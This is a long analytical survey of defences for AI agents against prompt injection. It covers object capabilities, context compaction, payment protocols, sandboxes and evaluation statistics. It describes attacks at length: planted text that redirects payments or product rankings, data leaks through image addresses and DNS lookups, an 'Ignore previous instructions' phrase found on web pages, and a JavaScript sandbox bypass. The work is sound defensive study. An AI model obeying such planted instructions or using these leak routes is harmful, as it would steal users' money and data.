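Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that issued the same permissions at the same moments but never revoked them. In one test, both completed all 10 runs without exceeding the contract. When the agent later tried to read the extra file again, PORTICO refused in all 10 runs, while the other version always allowed it. In another test, a live model received a planted instruction to reuse an expired permission to change files, alter a code repository's history or settings, or contact a network host. PORTICO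 blocked all six attempts, while the version without revocation carried them all out.

These results mostly confirm that revocation works as specified, since the comparison system had no means of revoking anything. They do not measure how often attackers exploit leftover permissions. They show more clearly that revocation can keep an agent from finishing its tasks. In 42 runs on real software projects, PORTICO completed 31 tasks and the version without revocation completed all 42. Some contracts ended access too early or gave the agent no way to regain it, and some models did not request it again. Someone also has to write each contract, and Santos-Grueiro did not measure how long that takes.

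### When a summary replaces the user's words

Long tasks create another problem. A language model can read only a limited amount of text at once. When a conversation nears that limit, the harness has a model summarise the earlier part and continues from the summary. This is called context compaction. *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction* (Fei, Fei and colleagues, 2026) recorded 1,108 automatic compactions in the coding agents Claude Code and Codex. The harness inserted the summary as a user message every time.

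A system that derives permissions from the latest user message can be misled if it mistakes a summary of the conversation for that message. Suppose a user asks a banking agent how much they spent in March, and one transaction contains an instruction to pay an attacker. Progent blocks the payment because the user's question doesn't require one. The conversation then grows too long and has to be summarized, and the summary lists the blocked payment as unfinished work. When the user says "continue", Progent treats the summary as the user's request and writes a new policy that permits the payment to the attacker.

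Progent normally writes its policy once per session, which would avoid this error. But Fei and colleagues found that an agent with a policy fixed at the first request completed the second task in only 7 of 60 two-task sessions, compared with 41 of 60 when Progent wrote a new policy for each request. They ran their attacks with per-request policies.

In one test, the summary led Progent to name the attacker's account, email address or web address in 16 of 30 new policies. When the harness supplied the same summaries as tool results instead of user messages, none of 28 policies did so. Across 100 attacked cases, 31 attacks succeeded after compaction with Progent and 33 without any defence. A small model, gpt-4o-mini, wrote those summaries and ran the agent.

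Stronger models usually flagged planted instructions in their summaries, and the resulting policies rarely permitted them. The models were much worse at flagging false data. In a further test, the user gave the landlord's account number and asked the agent what a notice said. The notice, written by the attacker, stated a different account number without any instruction. After compaction, the user asked the agent to pay the month's rent. When GPT-4o wrote the policies, 91% of them (290 of 320) permitted payment to the attacker's account. With GPT-5.5, 59% did. Policies derived from the user's own messages never permitted it. When the researchers let an agent act on 80 of these summaries and their policies, it paid the attacker in 33 cases.

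Fei and colleagues proved a limit on any system that judges text without knowing who wrote it. Let `p_L` be the probability that the policy permits a payment to the account in a record when a legitimate source wrote the record, and `p_A` the probability when an attacker did. `P_L` and `P_A` are the probability distributions of everything the system reads in the two cases. Then:

`p_L − p_A ≤ TV(P_L, P_A)`

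`TV` is the total variation distance, which is 0 when two distributions are identical and 1 when they never overlap. For any given text, the system permits the payment with some fixed probability, whoever wrote the text. Its average behaviour in the two cases can therefore differ only as much as the texts do. If a forged notice looks exactly like a real one, the system will accept both equally often, even with a better prompt or a stronger model.

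The proposed remedy keeps the user's messages separate from the summary of the conversation. The harness attaches a cryptographic tag to each user message when it arrives, and copies the messages unchanged when it compacts the conversation. Before a model writes a new policy, ordinary code checks that the tags are valid, the messages are in order and none are missing. The model writing the policy is given only those messages, while the agent still reads the summary. If a check fails, the policy permits nothing.

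No attack succeeded in the 40 attacked cases where the agent read the summary but its policy came from the authenticated messages. The agent completed 19 of the users' tasks when the harness supplied the summary as a tool result, compared with 27 of 40 when it could read the full, uncompacted conversation. Eight attacks designed to alter the authenticated messages also failed. Fei and colleagues tested replayed sessions, not a commercial product. The remedy doesn't help when the user relies on a document for the account number, because the number isn't in the user's messages.

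Developers can also fix the labelling. OpenAI changed Codex's automatic reviewer so that it attributes summaries to the assistant instead of the user. In tests with a rewritten summary, the earlier version approved 5 of 33 attacker calls and the later version approved none. IntentCap treats all user messages as the user's intent, so it would probably treat a summary that way too if the harness labelled it as a user message.

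### Signed consent to a manipulated choice

Google's Agent Payments Protocol, AP2, uses digital signatures to record what a user has agreed to buy. When the user is present, they approve an Intent Mandate that describes the purchase, a Cart Mandate that lists the item and final price, and a Payment Mandate that authorises the transfer. Altering a signed mandate invalidates its signature.

Debi, Zhu and Sen Gupta (2026), in *Whispers of Wealth*, tested whether a dishonest seller could influence the purchase before the user signs. They built an AP2 shopping agent with Gemini 2.5 Flash and asked it for basketball shoes to use outdoors. In 10 trials without an attack, it ranked suitable products first. They then hid an instruction in one product's description telling the agent to rank that product first. The agent did so in all 10 trials, and the mandates remained valid. In 6 of them, the product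 clearly conflicted with the user's request, such as a preferred brand.

The test used one request and one model, with no reported human approvers. It shows that a seller could control the ranking, but not how many people would have bought the shoes. An attentive buyer might notice the wrong brand in the cart, but would have less reason to object to a suitable but overpriced pair. If they signed, the signature would later be evidence that they had agreed to the purchase.

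Debi and colleagues also tried to get another customer's data by typing instructions to the agent, and succeeded in 2 of 10 trials. In a typical failure, the system accepted a claimed identity without verifying it again. Object capabilities could prevent this if the agent held a reference only to the signed-in customer's record, because typing another customer's name would not give the agent access to that customer's record.

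References can't correct the ranking in the same way. *Beyond the Mandate* (Aviv et al., 2026) analysed a later version of AP2 and found that its mandates still protect a transaction only after signing, not the messages and tool results that shape it beforehand. A signed price limit or a required brand would let ordinary code reject some manipulated carts. But the agent would still have to use the sellers' descriptions to choose among the shoes that met those conditions.

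## What audits, red teams and real deployments have shown

Most of the evidence so far comes from prototypes that their own designers tested. Outside agent research, programmers have spent several decades building object capabilities into desktops, operating systems, web pages and aircraft, and outsiders have sometimes tried to break those systems.

### The 2002 review of the DarpaBrowser

The DarpaBrowser was a web browser written in E, an object-capability language that Miller and others developed. It ran under CapDesk, the experimental desktop with the trusted file chooser. The browser's renderer, the component that turns a page's code into what the user sees, could be a plug-in from someone the user had no reason to trust. The browser therefore treated the renderer as a component that might turn hostile and should hold few references, much as the rebuilt invoice assistant treats its mail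 reader.

In 2002, David Wagner and Dean Tribble carried out a security review funded by DARPA, the US military's research agency. Miller acknowledges that they found "many vulnerabilities", but they were still encouraging about the approach. Their conclusion, reproduced on the E project's website, ERights, describes the browser task as "at or beyond the state of the art in security". They thought E made it easier to build boundaries between components that distrust each other, though many questions remained open.

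The review was only partly independent, because Tribble had worked on E. ERights credits him with a component that sped up E's interpreter, and the developers adopted that component before the review began. Inside knowledge probably helps a reviewer find flaws, but it may also make him more sympathetic to the design, so the vulnerabilities the review found are stronger evidence than its favourable conclusion.

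They also show that programmers can hand out the wrong references even when the rule about references is sound. E relied on existing Java libraries that weren't designed for capabilities, so E's developers had to "tame" each library by making it follow capability rules before E programs could use it. Miller claims only that taming gives some confidence, under some circumstances, that old code stays within its proper authority. TACIT's programmers take on the same job whenever they mark a library module as safe.

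CapDesk had to hold all of the user's authority to hand out parts of it, so a flaw in CapDesk could expose everything. If the user started another program outside CapDesk, that program kept the user's full authority and could undo the protection. An agent's harness has the same weaknesses. Miller also calls the email client the worst case among the programs ordinary people run, because even the least authority it needs is a dangerous combination. An assistant that reads email and also pays bills needs even more authority.

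None of this led to wide use. Four years after the review, Miller still called the DarpaBrowser a proof of concept and not yet a practical browser. EROS, a capability-based operating system developed between 1991 and 2005, was never used outside research.

Polaris, a related project, required less of its users because it ran ordinary Windows programs such as Excel without changes. It ran them in separate accounts that started with little authority. When the user opened a spreadsheet, Polaris gave Excel's account access to that file. Miller reports that users regularly left macros switched on because they no longer feared their documents. This suggests that people found the system convenient, though it doesn't show how many attacks Polaris stopped. Polaris also couldn't divide authority inside Excel, so every macro could use whatever authority Excel had received, a problem coding agents also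 have with the shell.

### A helicopter with a hostile camera

DARPA's HACMS programme, which began in 2012, provides much stronger evidence about the mechanism. Its engineers rebuilt the software of drones and other vehicles using methods meant to rule out whole classes of flaws. A red team of professional attackers then tried to break in.

Some of the vehicles used seL4, a small operating-system kernel that controls memory and communication through capabilities. Its developers had produced a machine-checked proof that the kernel's C code meets its specification. They later proved that the kernel enforces the access rules given to it. These proofs assume that the hardware works correctly and do not cover timing channels.

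In the best-known trial, engineers gave attackers full control of a Linux virtual machine that ran the camera software on Boeing's Unmanned Little Bird, a helicopter that can fly without a pilot. The attackers failed to break out of the virtual machine or disrupt the helicopter's flight.

The trial is a good precedent for agents because it assumed that the attacker already controlled one component, as someone who hijacks a model does. The proofs strengthen the evidence from the red team's failure because they also cover attacks on the kernel that nobody tried. But HACMS combined seL4 with other methods, including code that engineers generated from verified designs, so we can't attribute the result to capabilities alone.

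Permissions are also easier to specify for a helicopter than for an AI agent. The helicopter's engineers decided in advance which components could communicate, and the camera had the same job on every flight. An office assistant may need access to a mailbox for one request and a bank account for the next. The trial tested whether attackers could escape the compartment, but not what harm they could do through its permitted output. A hijacked camera could send false pictures to the operator, and the kernel would deliver them. A hijacked agent could similarly produce a misleading summary or an inflated invoice without exceeding its permissions.

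### Capsicum and the cost of changing programs

In the example of the two copying commands, `cat` received references to two open files but still ran with all of its user's authority. Capsicum, an addition to the FreeBSD operating system, lets a program give up that extra authority. The program opens what it needs and then makes the `cap_enter` system call. From then on, the kernel blocks any request that uses a global name, such as a file path or a process number. The program can use only the references it already holds or later receives, and neither it nor any process it starts can lift the restriction.

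FreeBSD, a mainstream operating system, has included the object-capability mechanism Capsicum for more than a decade. Capsicum's designers tested it on Chromium, the open-source browser behind Chrome, which already sandboxed its renderers differently on each operating system. Those older sandboxes took from a few hundred lines of code or policy to 22,000 lines of C++, while Capsicum took about 100. The designers also found significant vulnerabilities in all the older sandboxes, some caused by their design and others by incorrect use. Although the designers were comparing their own system with its rivals, the difference in size is hard to dismiss.

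Other programs were harder to convert than the line counts suggest. `tcpdump`, which displays network traffic, is a good candidate for isolation because it reads data that any stranger can send. Putting it into capability mode took only a few lines, but it could then no longer look up machine names, because lookups need files and network services that it had not opened in advance. A separate helper had to do them. Agent developers can expect the same difficulty with shell tools, many of which open configuration files, caches and network connections that are easy to overlook.

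Capsicum has had flaws too. In 2023, FreeBSD's developers fixed a system call that copies data between files. The call checked that the program could read the first file and write to the second, but not whether it could choose a position within the file. A program with permission to write only at the current position could therefore overwrite any part of the file. The references were still unforgeable, but Capsicum lacked complete mediation because this call had a weaker check than the other routes to the file.

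Google's engineers also ported Capsicum to Linux, but the Linux maintainers never merged it into the main kernel. Most agents run their tools on Linux, so agent developers generally have to combine other isolation features to get a similar result.

Programs can also leave unforgeable references in places nobody intended. CHERI, a processor design from Cambridge and SRI International, protects capabilities in hardware, so a program can't create one from an ordinary number. But on two operating systems built for CHERI, an attacker who starts with one capability can search the memory it reaches for old ones that programs left there, then search the memory those reach. The attacker collects far more authority than the programmer intended, even though the hardware enforces each capability correctly. An agent harness that keeps old references in a shared workspace could have the same weakness.

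### Caja and hardened JavaScript

Google's Caja project began applying object capabilities to web pages in 2008. Normally, a third-party script can do everything the page that includes it can do. Caja rewrote third-party HTML, CSS and JavaScript into a restricted form, and the site gave the rewritten code references to the objects that code was allowed to use.

Google archived Caja in January 2021 because it had known vulnerabilities and wasn't maintained well enough to keep up with web security research. A rewriter like Caja protects a page only if it interprets code exactly as the browser will, so without maintenance, any new browser feature could open a way around it. Google stopped paying for that maintenance, but the principle behind Caja didn't fail.

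Its successor, hardened JavaScript, relies less on rewriting code. It freezes the language's built-in objects so that one script can't tamper with what another relies on, and it runs untrusted code in a compartment that holds only the references it receives. Cryptocurrency wallet software uses it to limit the damage that a malicious add-on or library can do. The potential market is large, since Van Cutsem's *Designing “least-authority” JavaScript apps* lists mobile, desktop, server, database and embedded software among the places where JavaScript now runs.

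A flaw from 2023 in the hardened system let a program with no references load modules from the surrounding system and, in some configurations, run arbitrary code. JavaScript's `import(...)` expression, which loads other code, is part of the language's grammar, so a program can use it without holding any reference. The hardened system therefore searched the program's text for it, but skipped any `import` that followed a dot, because a dot normally means a call to an object's own method of that name. JavaScript also uses three dots to unpack a value, so the search missed `{...import(x)}`.

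This flaw is relevant to agents that write code, because the early version of TACIT also enforced its safe subset by searching for forbidden text. Moving that check into the compiler was an improvement, since the compiler parses the program instead of matching patterns in its text. Attackers will still look for a trick like the three dots that gets past the compiler.

### What companies have released for agents

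Chrome now includes an agent called auto browse, which uses Google's Gemini model to operate websites for the user. Chromium's *Chrome Security 2026 Q1 Update* (2026) confirms that it launched with several layers of defence. Chrome's security team adjusts these layers based on real use and has built more collections of attacks to test them.

Google described the design in December 2025. One layer limits the agent to sites relevant to the task, and separates those it may only read from those where it may also click and type. In another, a second model judges each proposed action without seeing the web page. Chrome also asks the user before sensitive steps such as a purchase. The site lists are a permission table kept by the harness, and Google keeps untrusted page content away from the component that decides which sites are relevant. This makes planted text less likely to widen the agent's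 access, although a site that belongs on the list can still contain an attacker's text.

Cloudflare, which runs other companies' code on its servers, comes closer to the classical model. In September 2025 it introduced Code Mode, in which a language model writes a program that calls several tools. The program runs in an isolate, a lightweight sandbox without general internet access, and can act outside it only through objects called "bindings" that the developer passes in. The software behind a binding adds the password or key, so the program never receives it and can't leak it.

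Bindings are classical object capabilities, but unlike TACIT's types, they don't track data, so a program can copy customer records from one binding into a message sent through another. A binding can also grant too much access. If it represents a whole tool server, a hijacked model can use every tool on it.

Amazon and Microsoft offer checks that developers can add to their own agents. Amazon's policy layer for Bedrock AgentCore, its service for running agents, places a gateway between the agent and its tools. The gateway checks each call against rules written in Cedar, Amazon's language for access policies. The model can't rewrite these rules, but they cover only the calls that go through the gateway. Microsoft has released code for FIDES, its system for checking provenance labels.

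These products differ in maturity. Auto browse is a launched consumer feature, while FIDES is software that developers build on. Amazon introduced its policy layer as a preview, and Cloudflare first offered its sandbox for model-written programs as a closed test. A launch shows that a company considers a product ready for customers, but it is much weaker evidence of security than a failed attempt by outsiders to break the product. Most of the public evidence for these four products comes from their makers' own descriptions and tests. In 2026, agents being tested reached outside systems, so the containment layer itself needs testing.

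### Frameworks that check the tool and not the payment

Developers who add no such layer rely on whatever their agent framework provides. Mellafe Zuvic, an independent security researcher, read the public source code of specific versions of three widely used options: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to a payment company. He examined what happens between the model writing a tool call and the tool running.

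LangChain, LlamaIndex and Stripe's toolkit all limit which tools an agent can call, but by default they don't check whether the values in a call are allowed. LangChain looks up the tool by name, usually checks that the arguments have the right form, and runs it. LlamaIndex does much the same. Stripe's toolkit adds a list of permitted actions and a restricted key, but within those limits it forwards whatever amount, currency and customer the model supplied. Mellafe Zuvic did not examine what Stripe's servers may check afterwards.

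He demonstrated the gap with a mock merchant. He fixed the model's output to be a call that changed the merchant's payout account to `acct_ATTACKER_999`. LangChain made the change because the account number was a well-formed string and the agent had the tool. He then sent the same call through ScopeGate, a gate he had written that checks the account against a list the operator set in advance. ScopeGate blocked the call before the tool ran.

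Mellafe Zuvic calls this a gap in the defaults and doesn't claim to have found a formal vulnerability in any of the products. Developers can add the missing check, but busy ones end up with the defaults, and the effect could be serious if the model's requests are often wrong.

He therefore also reports how often 27 models attempted an unauthorised action when planted text presented it as necessary for the user's task. The 12 cheaper models, which firms might choose for high-volume work, did so in 60.3% of trials on average. The 15 flagship models averaged 18.9%, though some of them also had high rates. The wording of the planted text greatly affected the results. Mistral Large attempted the action in 2.7% of trials when the text simply demanded it and in 45.9% when the text tied it to the task. For GLM-4.7, the rate rose from 28.3% to 100%. These figures count attempts in a sandbox, not actual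 thefts.

ScopeGate blocked all 48 prepared attempts to bypass it, including account names with invisible characters, arguments of the wrong type, and misspelled tool names. Preparing these attempts was useful mainly because it exposed a bug in an earlier version. The bug involved NaN, a special value computers use for results that aren't numbers. NaN never counts as greater than the payment limit, so a gate that refuses only amounts above the limit lets it through. The repaired gate accepts only finite numbers between zero and the limit.

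In a further test, the model GLM-5.2 made 40 attempts to get past the gate and was told the reason for each refusal. The gate denied all 29 unauthorised calls. Of the other attempts, 9 were malformed and 2 were harmless calls. This is encouraging, but 40 attempts are few, and the same person wrote the gate, the policy and the tests. In a separate check, the gate allowed all 10 legitimate calls, but 10 calls are too few to estimate how often it would obstruct real work.

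As with the rebuilt invoice assistant, object capabilities would have stopped the payout attack only if a developer had restricted the reference to allow only the merchant's verified accounts. ScopeGate's list achieves the same result in this case.

### Browsers that lend the agent the user's logins

Several companies sell browsers with a built-in agent that can read and operate web pages. *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities*, by the security company Trail of Bits, describes successful attacks on several of these products. Trail of Bits did not name them because their makers declined to coordinate disclosure. It also gave no success rates, so its work shows that the attacks are possible but not how often they would succeed or which browsers are safest.

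The main cause was ambient authority. When a person logs in to a website, the browser stores a cookie, a small piece of data that identifies the person on later visits. The agents that Trail of Bits tested reused these cookies automatically, so an agent asked to summarize a stranger's page could also open the user's account on another site, although the summary didn't require it. Web developers have dealt for decades with a similar attack, in which a malicious page makes the user's browser send a request to a site where the user is logged in.

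| Attack | What the agent did | Would object capabilities have stopped it? |
|---|---|---|
| False information | Repeated an invented story from a document, in which Yuri Gagarin was first on the Moon | No, because the attack needs no action |
| Silent login | Opened a link that logged the user in to the attacker's account | Yes, if a summary task includes no reference for opening links |
| Leak from the conversation | Put the user's name into a web address and opened it | Yes, if the task includes no reference for sending requests |
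| Leak from another site | Read a name from a site where the user was logged in, then sent it out | Yes, if the task can reach only the page to be summarised |
| Leak through search | Inferred the user's location from personalised results, then sent it out | Yes, if the task includes no reference for sending requests |
| Leak from private messages | Followed instructions in an Instagram message and sent out contact names or message extracts | Partly, because the task requires reading the messages |
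| False history | Added illegal sites to the user's browsing history | Yes, if the agent has no access to the history |

The favourable answers depend on a narrow grant for each request, not one general reference for operating the user's browser.

The Instagram attack would be hard to stop even with a narrow grant. The user asks for a summary of recent messages, so the agent has to read them, including the attacker's. Without general internet access, the agent can't send the messages to the attacker's server, but if it can reply on Instagram, it can send them to the attacker there. A provenance policy could block replies that contain other people's messages, but it would also block some legitimate replies.

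Lists of approved sites also gave less protection than they appeared to. Some agents could contact only permitted domains, such as Wikipedia's, but Trail of Bits made one open an address like `leaked-data.wikipedia.org`. Although no such site exists, the computer still looks up the name in the internet's directory service, and anyone who can observe that unencrypted lookup can read the secret in the name. In another attack, the agent entered the secret into Google Search next to unusual words, and the attacker watched for those words in a Google service that shows site owners which searches lead to their pages. An object-capability design would have the same leak if it gave the agent a reference that accepts any name under `wikipedia.org`. A reference to a particular page would leave much less room for leaks.

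Trail of Bits proposes extending the web's same-origin policy, which stops a script from one website from reading another's data. The browser would list every origin, meaning every site or file, whose content the agent had read:

- With no origin on the list, the agent could make requests freely.
- With one origin, it could send requests only to that origin.
- With two or more, it could send none, since nobody can tell which origin influenced the model.

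This rule is a simple form of provenance tracking that ordinary code can enforce. It would block the leaks from one site to another. It would also stop an agent that had compared prices in two shops from buying in either, which is another case of label creep. It would not stop the Instagram leak whenever the agent can send messages there, because the data comes from and returns to the same origin. Trail of Bits presents the rule as a direction for further research, and nobody has shown how much ordinary browsing it would prevent.

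As a short-term measure, Trail of Bits recommends running the agent's tools in a separate browser that doesn't share the user's cookies or history. This immediately removes the ambient authority, but the agent also loses access to every service where the user is logged in, unless the user logs in again for it. That access is a large part of what the products offer.

The browser is also part of the trusted computing base, and many of these browsers use versions of Chromium that are weeks or months behind on security patches. An attacker could plant an instruction that sends the agent to a page that exploits an old flaw and takes over the browser. The attacker could then bypass the checks on the agent's tool calls.

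### An expired domain on Salesforce's list

Researchers at the security company Noma found a similar leak in Agentforce, Salesforce's product for building agents that work with customer records, and disclosed it in September 2025 under the name ForcedLeak.

The attack began with a contact form of the kind many companies have on their websites. Salesforce stores each enquiry as a record. The researchers typed an instruction into the form's description field and waited for an employee to ask the agent about the enquiry. The agent followed the instruction, looked up the details of other potential customers, and put them into the address of an image in its answer. When the employee's browser tried to fetch the image to display the answer, the request sent the details to the server named in the address.

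Salesforce had anticipated such leaks, and its pages let the browser load images only from approved domains. But one approved domain had expired. The researchers registered it for about $5, and the browser then treated their server as trusted. Salesforce has since recovered the domain and restricted its agents to a list of trusted addresses.

The approval was correct at first, but the list identified the server by its domain name, which later expired and passed to a new owner. A reference tied to the original server's cryptographic key would have stopped working when the domain expired. However, the web identifies servers by domain, and a new owner can easily get a valid certificate. A capability that merely wraps a web address would therefore have failed in the same way as the list.

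Object capabilities could have helped more at an earlier step, by limiting which records the agent could read. To answer a question about one enquiry, the agent needed only that enquiry's record and perhaps a few related ones. If it had held references to only those records, the planted instruction could not have made it retrieve the rest of the customer list, whatever happened to the domain. The agent would still need wider access when an employee asked for an overview of all recent enquiries, and the attacker could wait for that request.

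The leak also shows how easily a developer can miss an action with an outside effect. The agent wrote an answer without calling any tool for sending data, and another program turned part of the answer into a web request. A gateway that inspects only tool calls would not have detected the leak. Complete mediation has to include whatever displays the agent's output, or the harness has to remove active links and images first.

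### Planted instructions on the public web

Researchers carried out the attacks on the browsers and Agentforce. Criminals and pranksters also plant instructions. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* describes two companies' searches for such instructions.

Google searched a collection of web pages, which grows by two to three billion pages a month, for text planted to influence AI agents. It concentrated on blogs, forums, comment sections and other static pages, and left out social media. Some of the planted text was harmless, such as an instruction for an agent to write like a bird. Some was meant to steer search results or to keep agents away from a page's content. The more dangerous examples were instructions to reveal secret keys or delete the user's files. Google repeated the scan on several versions of a public web archive and found that the malicious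 category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026.

The security company Forcepoint searched for web pages containing phrases such as "Ignore previous instructions" and found several aimed at money. One included a complete PayPal transaction, with instructions for an agent that can make payments. Another tried to direct payments to a donation link. A third seemed to be a test, perhaps to see which agents would obey before the attacker tried something worse. Attackers had hidden such text from people by shrinking it to a single pixel, making it almost transparent, or putting it in comments and metadata that browsers don't display.

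Neither company found a sophisticated, coordinated campaign. Forcepoint did find the same templates on several domains, which suggests that some attackers share tools.

The 32% rise is good evidence that interest is growing, but it is a relative increase from a low base, so planted text is still rare. The searches also count planted text, not the agents that obeyed it, so we can't tell from them how much money or data anyone lost. They are probably worst at finding careful attacks, because neither covers private email, where the forged invoice would arrive, and an instruction worded to look like ordinary business would not contain the phrases that Forcepoint looked for.

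In most of the examples, attackers try to get an agent to do something the user never requested, and a narrow grant of authority handles those cases well. Forcepoint rates a browser assistant that only summarises as low-risk, and one that can send emails, run commands or make payments as a high-impact target. If agents with payment powers become common, attackers will have more reason to write text that targets the payments those agents are supposed to make.

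## What evidence would establish that a deployment is secure

Suppose a vendor offers the small firm an invoice assistant and reports that no attack succeeded in 949 benchmark cases. The owner can't tell from this figure whether the assistant can reach outside systems by a route the vendor's check doesn't cover, how much a thief could take through permitted payments, or who would spot a forged invoice when the software asks for approval.

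"Secure in practice" combines five claims, and each needs its own evidence. No standard sets pass marks for them. The pass marks below might suit a small firm, but a bank would need stricter ones.

| Claim | Test | Pass mark | Result that would refute it |
|---|---|---|---|
| The mechanism enforces its grant | Proof of the core rules, an audit of the remaining code, and a trial in which attackers control the model's output | The proof covers the deployed version, and attackers with the source code find no escape in an agreed period | One reproducible action outside the grant |
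| Every effect passes through the check | Set the check to refuse everything, then try to cause any outside effect | Independent records show no effect | One payment, file change or network request |
| The grant is narrow enough | Calculate the worst loss from permitted actions, then attack using only those actions | The worst loss stays below a limit the owner set beforehand, and the agent still completes an agreed share of its work | A permitted sequence of actions that costs more |
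| The people who approve are not fooled | Slip realistic fraudulent requests into ordinary work | The 95% upper bound on the share of frauds approved is below 5% | A 95% interval that lies wholly above 5% |
| Losses in use stay below a stated level | Incident records, with a count of the attacks that arrived | The 95% upper bound on losses is below that level | A 95% interval that lies wholly above that level |

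Many results will fall between the last two columns and leave the claim open.

### Testing the check itself

A proof covers only the parts it describes. An auditor could therefore list every component in the trusted computing base and record whether it has a proof, has passed a code review or is simply trusted. For TACIT, the list would include the compiler's safe mode, the library and the second model. Reviewers could then focus on the parts without proofs, particularly the modules programmers have marked as safe.

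Attackers should then write the agent's programs or tool calls themselves, instead of trying to persuade a model to write them. The attackers in the helicopter trial similarly began with full control of one component. Such a trial remains valid when the vendor replaces the model, because the result doesn't depend on how the model behaves.

Success rates mean little in this test. A check written in ordinary code gives the same answer whenever it receives the same call in the same state, so an attacker who finds one call it wrongly accepts can use that call every time. The payment gate that accepted NaN would have done very well in a test of 1,000 ordinary numbers. A useful report would describe the attackers' skill, their access to the source code, how many days they spent and which parts they examined.

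To test complete mediation, meaning that every action goes through the check, a tester can set the check to refuse everything and run a hostile program with the agent's usual tools. A separate machine records network traffic, including name lookups, and any changes to files or accounts. The test has to include the window that displays the agent's answers, because in the Salesforce attack the browser sent out the data while loading an image.

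Once the assistant is in use, the firm can compare the check's log with the bank's. Every payment in the bank's records should match one call that the check approved. TechRadar's *NIST published the script for rogue AI agents. What about the victims?*, an opinion piece by a co-founder of the security company Mitiga, recommends relying on logs that the receiving system creates and the agent can't alter. This is sound advice because a payment that bypassed the check won't appear in the check's log. The comparison can't reveal leaks through timing or other side channels.

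### Attacks confined to permitted actions

The firm can assess part of a grant without running a model, by assuming that the agent is hostile and calculating the largest loss it could cause. Suppose the agent can pay 40 approved suppliers up to €2,000 each per month. Together, these limits allow €80,000 a month. If the owner can afford to lose only €5,000 a month, the grant is too broad, and a monthly cap of €5,000 on all payments together would fix this. If the agent can also read the whole mailbox and write to any outsider, somebody has to estimate what leaking the whole mailbox would cost.

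Sometimes an agent's work requires a permission that could allow an unacceptable loss. Security then depends on how often an attacker can get the model to misuse that permission. Testers have to measure this with attacks limited to permitted actions, such as raising the amount of a payment or getting a bill paid twice.

An average success rate across different attack goals can hide how often the dangerous attacks succeed. *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations* describes tests by the Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), part of the US standards agency NIST. The agent used Claude 3.5 Sonnet, a model from 2024. Attacks with five different goals succeeded 57% of the time on average. One goal was to send a stranger a harmless email. Another, to download and run a malicious program, succeeded often and could enable further attacks. A third, to email out the user's five largest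 files, delete them and demand a ransom, succeeded less often but would do far more damage than the harmless email. A firm should therefore ask for a separate result for each goal.

The same test must also measure how many tasks the agent completes, because CaMeL had a low attack success rate on tampered tasks but a completion rate of only 13%.

### The June 2026 protocol for adaptive evaluation

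In June 2026, Narisetty and colleagues proposed a protocol for testing defences that check an agent's actions. It tests systems that outsiders can run, such as Progent and CaMeL, on the AgentDojo and Agent Security Bench benchmarks. The attacker knows the policy and adapts to it. The protocol uses four kinds of attack, shown here with examples for the invoice assistant.

| Attack | Example |
|---|---|
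| Optimise the planted text against the deployed check | Reword an invoice until the model that writes the policy adds the attacker as a payee |
| Forge provenance | Get the attacker's account number into a supplier record that the policy trusts |
| Deceive the person who approves exceptions | Send a believable notice of new bank details before the forged invoice arrives |
| Probe for side channels | Work out a secret from which requests the agent makes and which fail |

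Testers then measure how often the harmful action occurs and how many tasks the agent completes compared with an undefended agent. They also record how often the agent asks the user to approve an action and how much the check adds to running costs.

The approval rate is worth reporting because a defence can otherwise look perfect by passing every difficult decision to the user. Suppose the assistant handles 40 invoices a week and asks the owner to approve about 10 of them, a rate of 25%. If it refers every forged invoice to the owner, who approves 30% of them, those forgeries get paid. A benchmark that counts a request for approval as a successful defence would record none of these payments as failures. The 30% is illustrative, but it is close to Yan's result for people who approved every action by hand, excluding the call to the airport.

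The protocol sets no pass mark and no minimum number of cases or attempts. Its list of attacks omits those that use only permitted actions. Narisetty and colleagues reported no approval rate for their own small test of Progent.

Security tests should measure attacks on tasks that weren't used to develop them, because otherwise testers can't tell whether the attacks work elsewhere. CAISI staff, working with the UK AI Security Institute, developed new attacks on some of AgentDojo's office tasks and measured them on others. The strongest new attack succeeded 81% of the time, compared with 11% for the strongest existing attack. The new attacks also worked in AgentDojo's other three environments.

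### How many attacks a test needs

Even if every attack in a test fails, the true success rate may be above zero. Let `p` be that rate, and suppose testers make `n` independent attempts. The chance that they all fail is `(1 − p)^n`. Setting this equal to 5% gives the 95% upper bound, the highest rate that is still reasonably compatible with the result. For large `n`, it is approximately:

`p ≈ 3/n`

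If none of n independent attempts succeeds, the 95% upper bound on the success rate is about 3/n, where 3 approximates the natural logarithm of 20. Testers therefore need about 3,000 attempts without a success to lower the bound to 0.1%. The vendor's 949 cases give a bound of 0.3%, and the 120 planted instructions in the TACIT experiment give 2.5% for each model.

When some attacks succeed, testers can use the Wilson interval, a standard range for a rate estimated from a sample. With `s` successes, `p̂ = s/n` and `z = 1.96`, the 95% interval is:

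`(p̂ + z²/2n ± z√(p̂(1 − p̂)/n + z²/4n²)) / (1 + z²/n)`

CapScope let through 3 attacks in 75 runs, or 4% (95% confidence interval about 1% to 11%). All three used text planted in `AGENTS.md`, which was tested in 15 of the runs, so the rate for that file was 20% (about 7% to 45%). The second interval matters more because an attacker who can choose where to plant text would choose the weakest place. But Bouras and colleagues could identify the weakest place only after seeing the results, so the 20% may be partly bad luck, which new runs on that file would test.

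Both intervals are probably too narrow, because the 75 runs are 25 cases repeated three times. If the three runs of a case always had the same outcome, the experiment would amount to 25 attempts, and a rate of 4% would have an interval of about 1% to 20%.

### Thousands of copies of one attack

Training an agent to resist a larger collection of attacks does not always make it more secure. *PIPETTE* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) studied PISmith and RL-Hammer, two tools that learn to write planted instructions. Against the small model Qwen3-4B, PISmith found 7,132 working attacks and RL-Hammer found 4,282. The researchers used reinforcement learning to train the model on each collection separately, then tried three new kinds of attack on 40 test cases. The most successful kind hijacked the agent in 19 cases after training on PISmith's collection and in 11 after training on RL-Hammer's.

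He and colleagues suspect that the larger collection mostly repeated a few strategies, such as telling the agent that the user's task is already finished. Both tools encourage variety but measure it by wording. RL-Hammer satisfied its variety measure by changing capitalization or adding irrelevant text, according to Zorz (2026) in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*.

He and colleagues measured strategies instead, by having a language model describe how each attack worked. They reduced the descriptions to recurring components and scored, from 0 to 1, how well these explained a separate family of attacks. As RL-Hammer's collection against Qwen3-4B grew, its score levelled off near 0.20. PISmith's score stagnated or fell after an early stage. Thousands of further attacks apparently added few new strategies.

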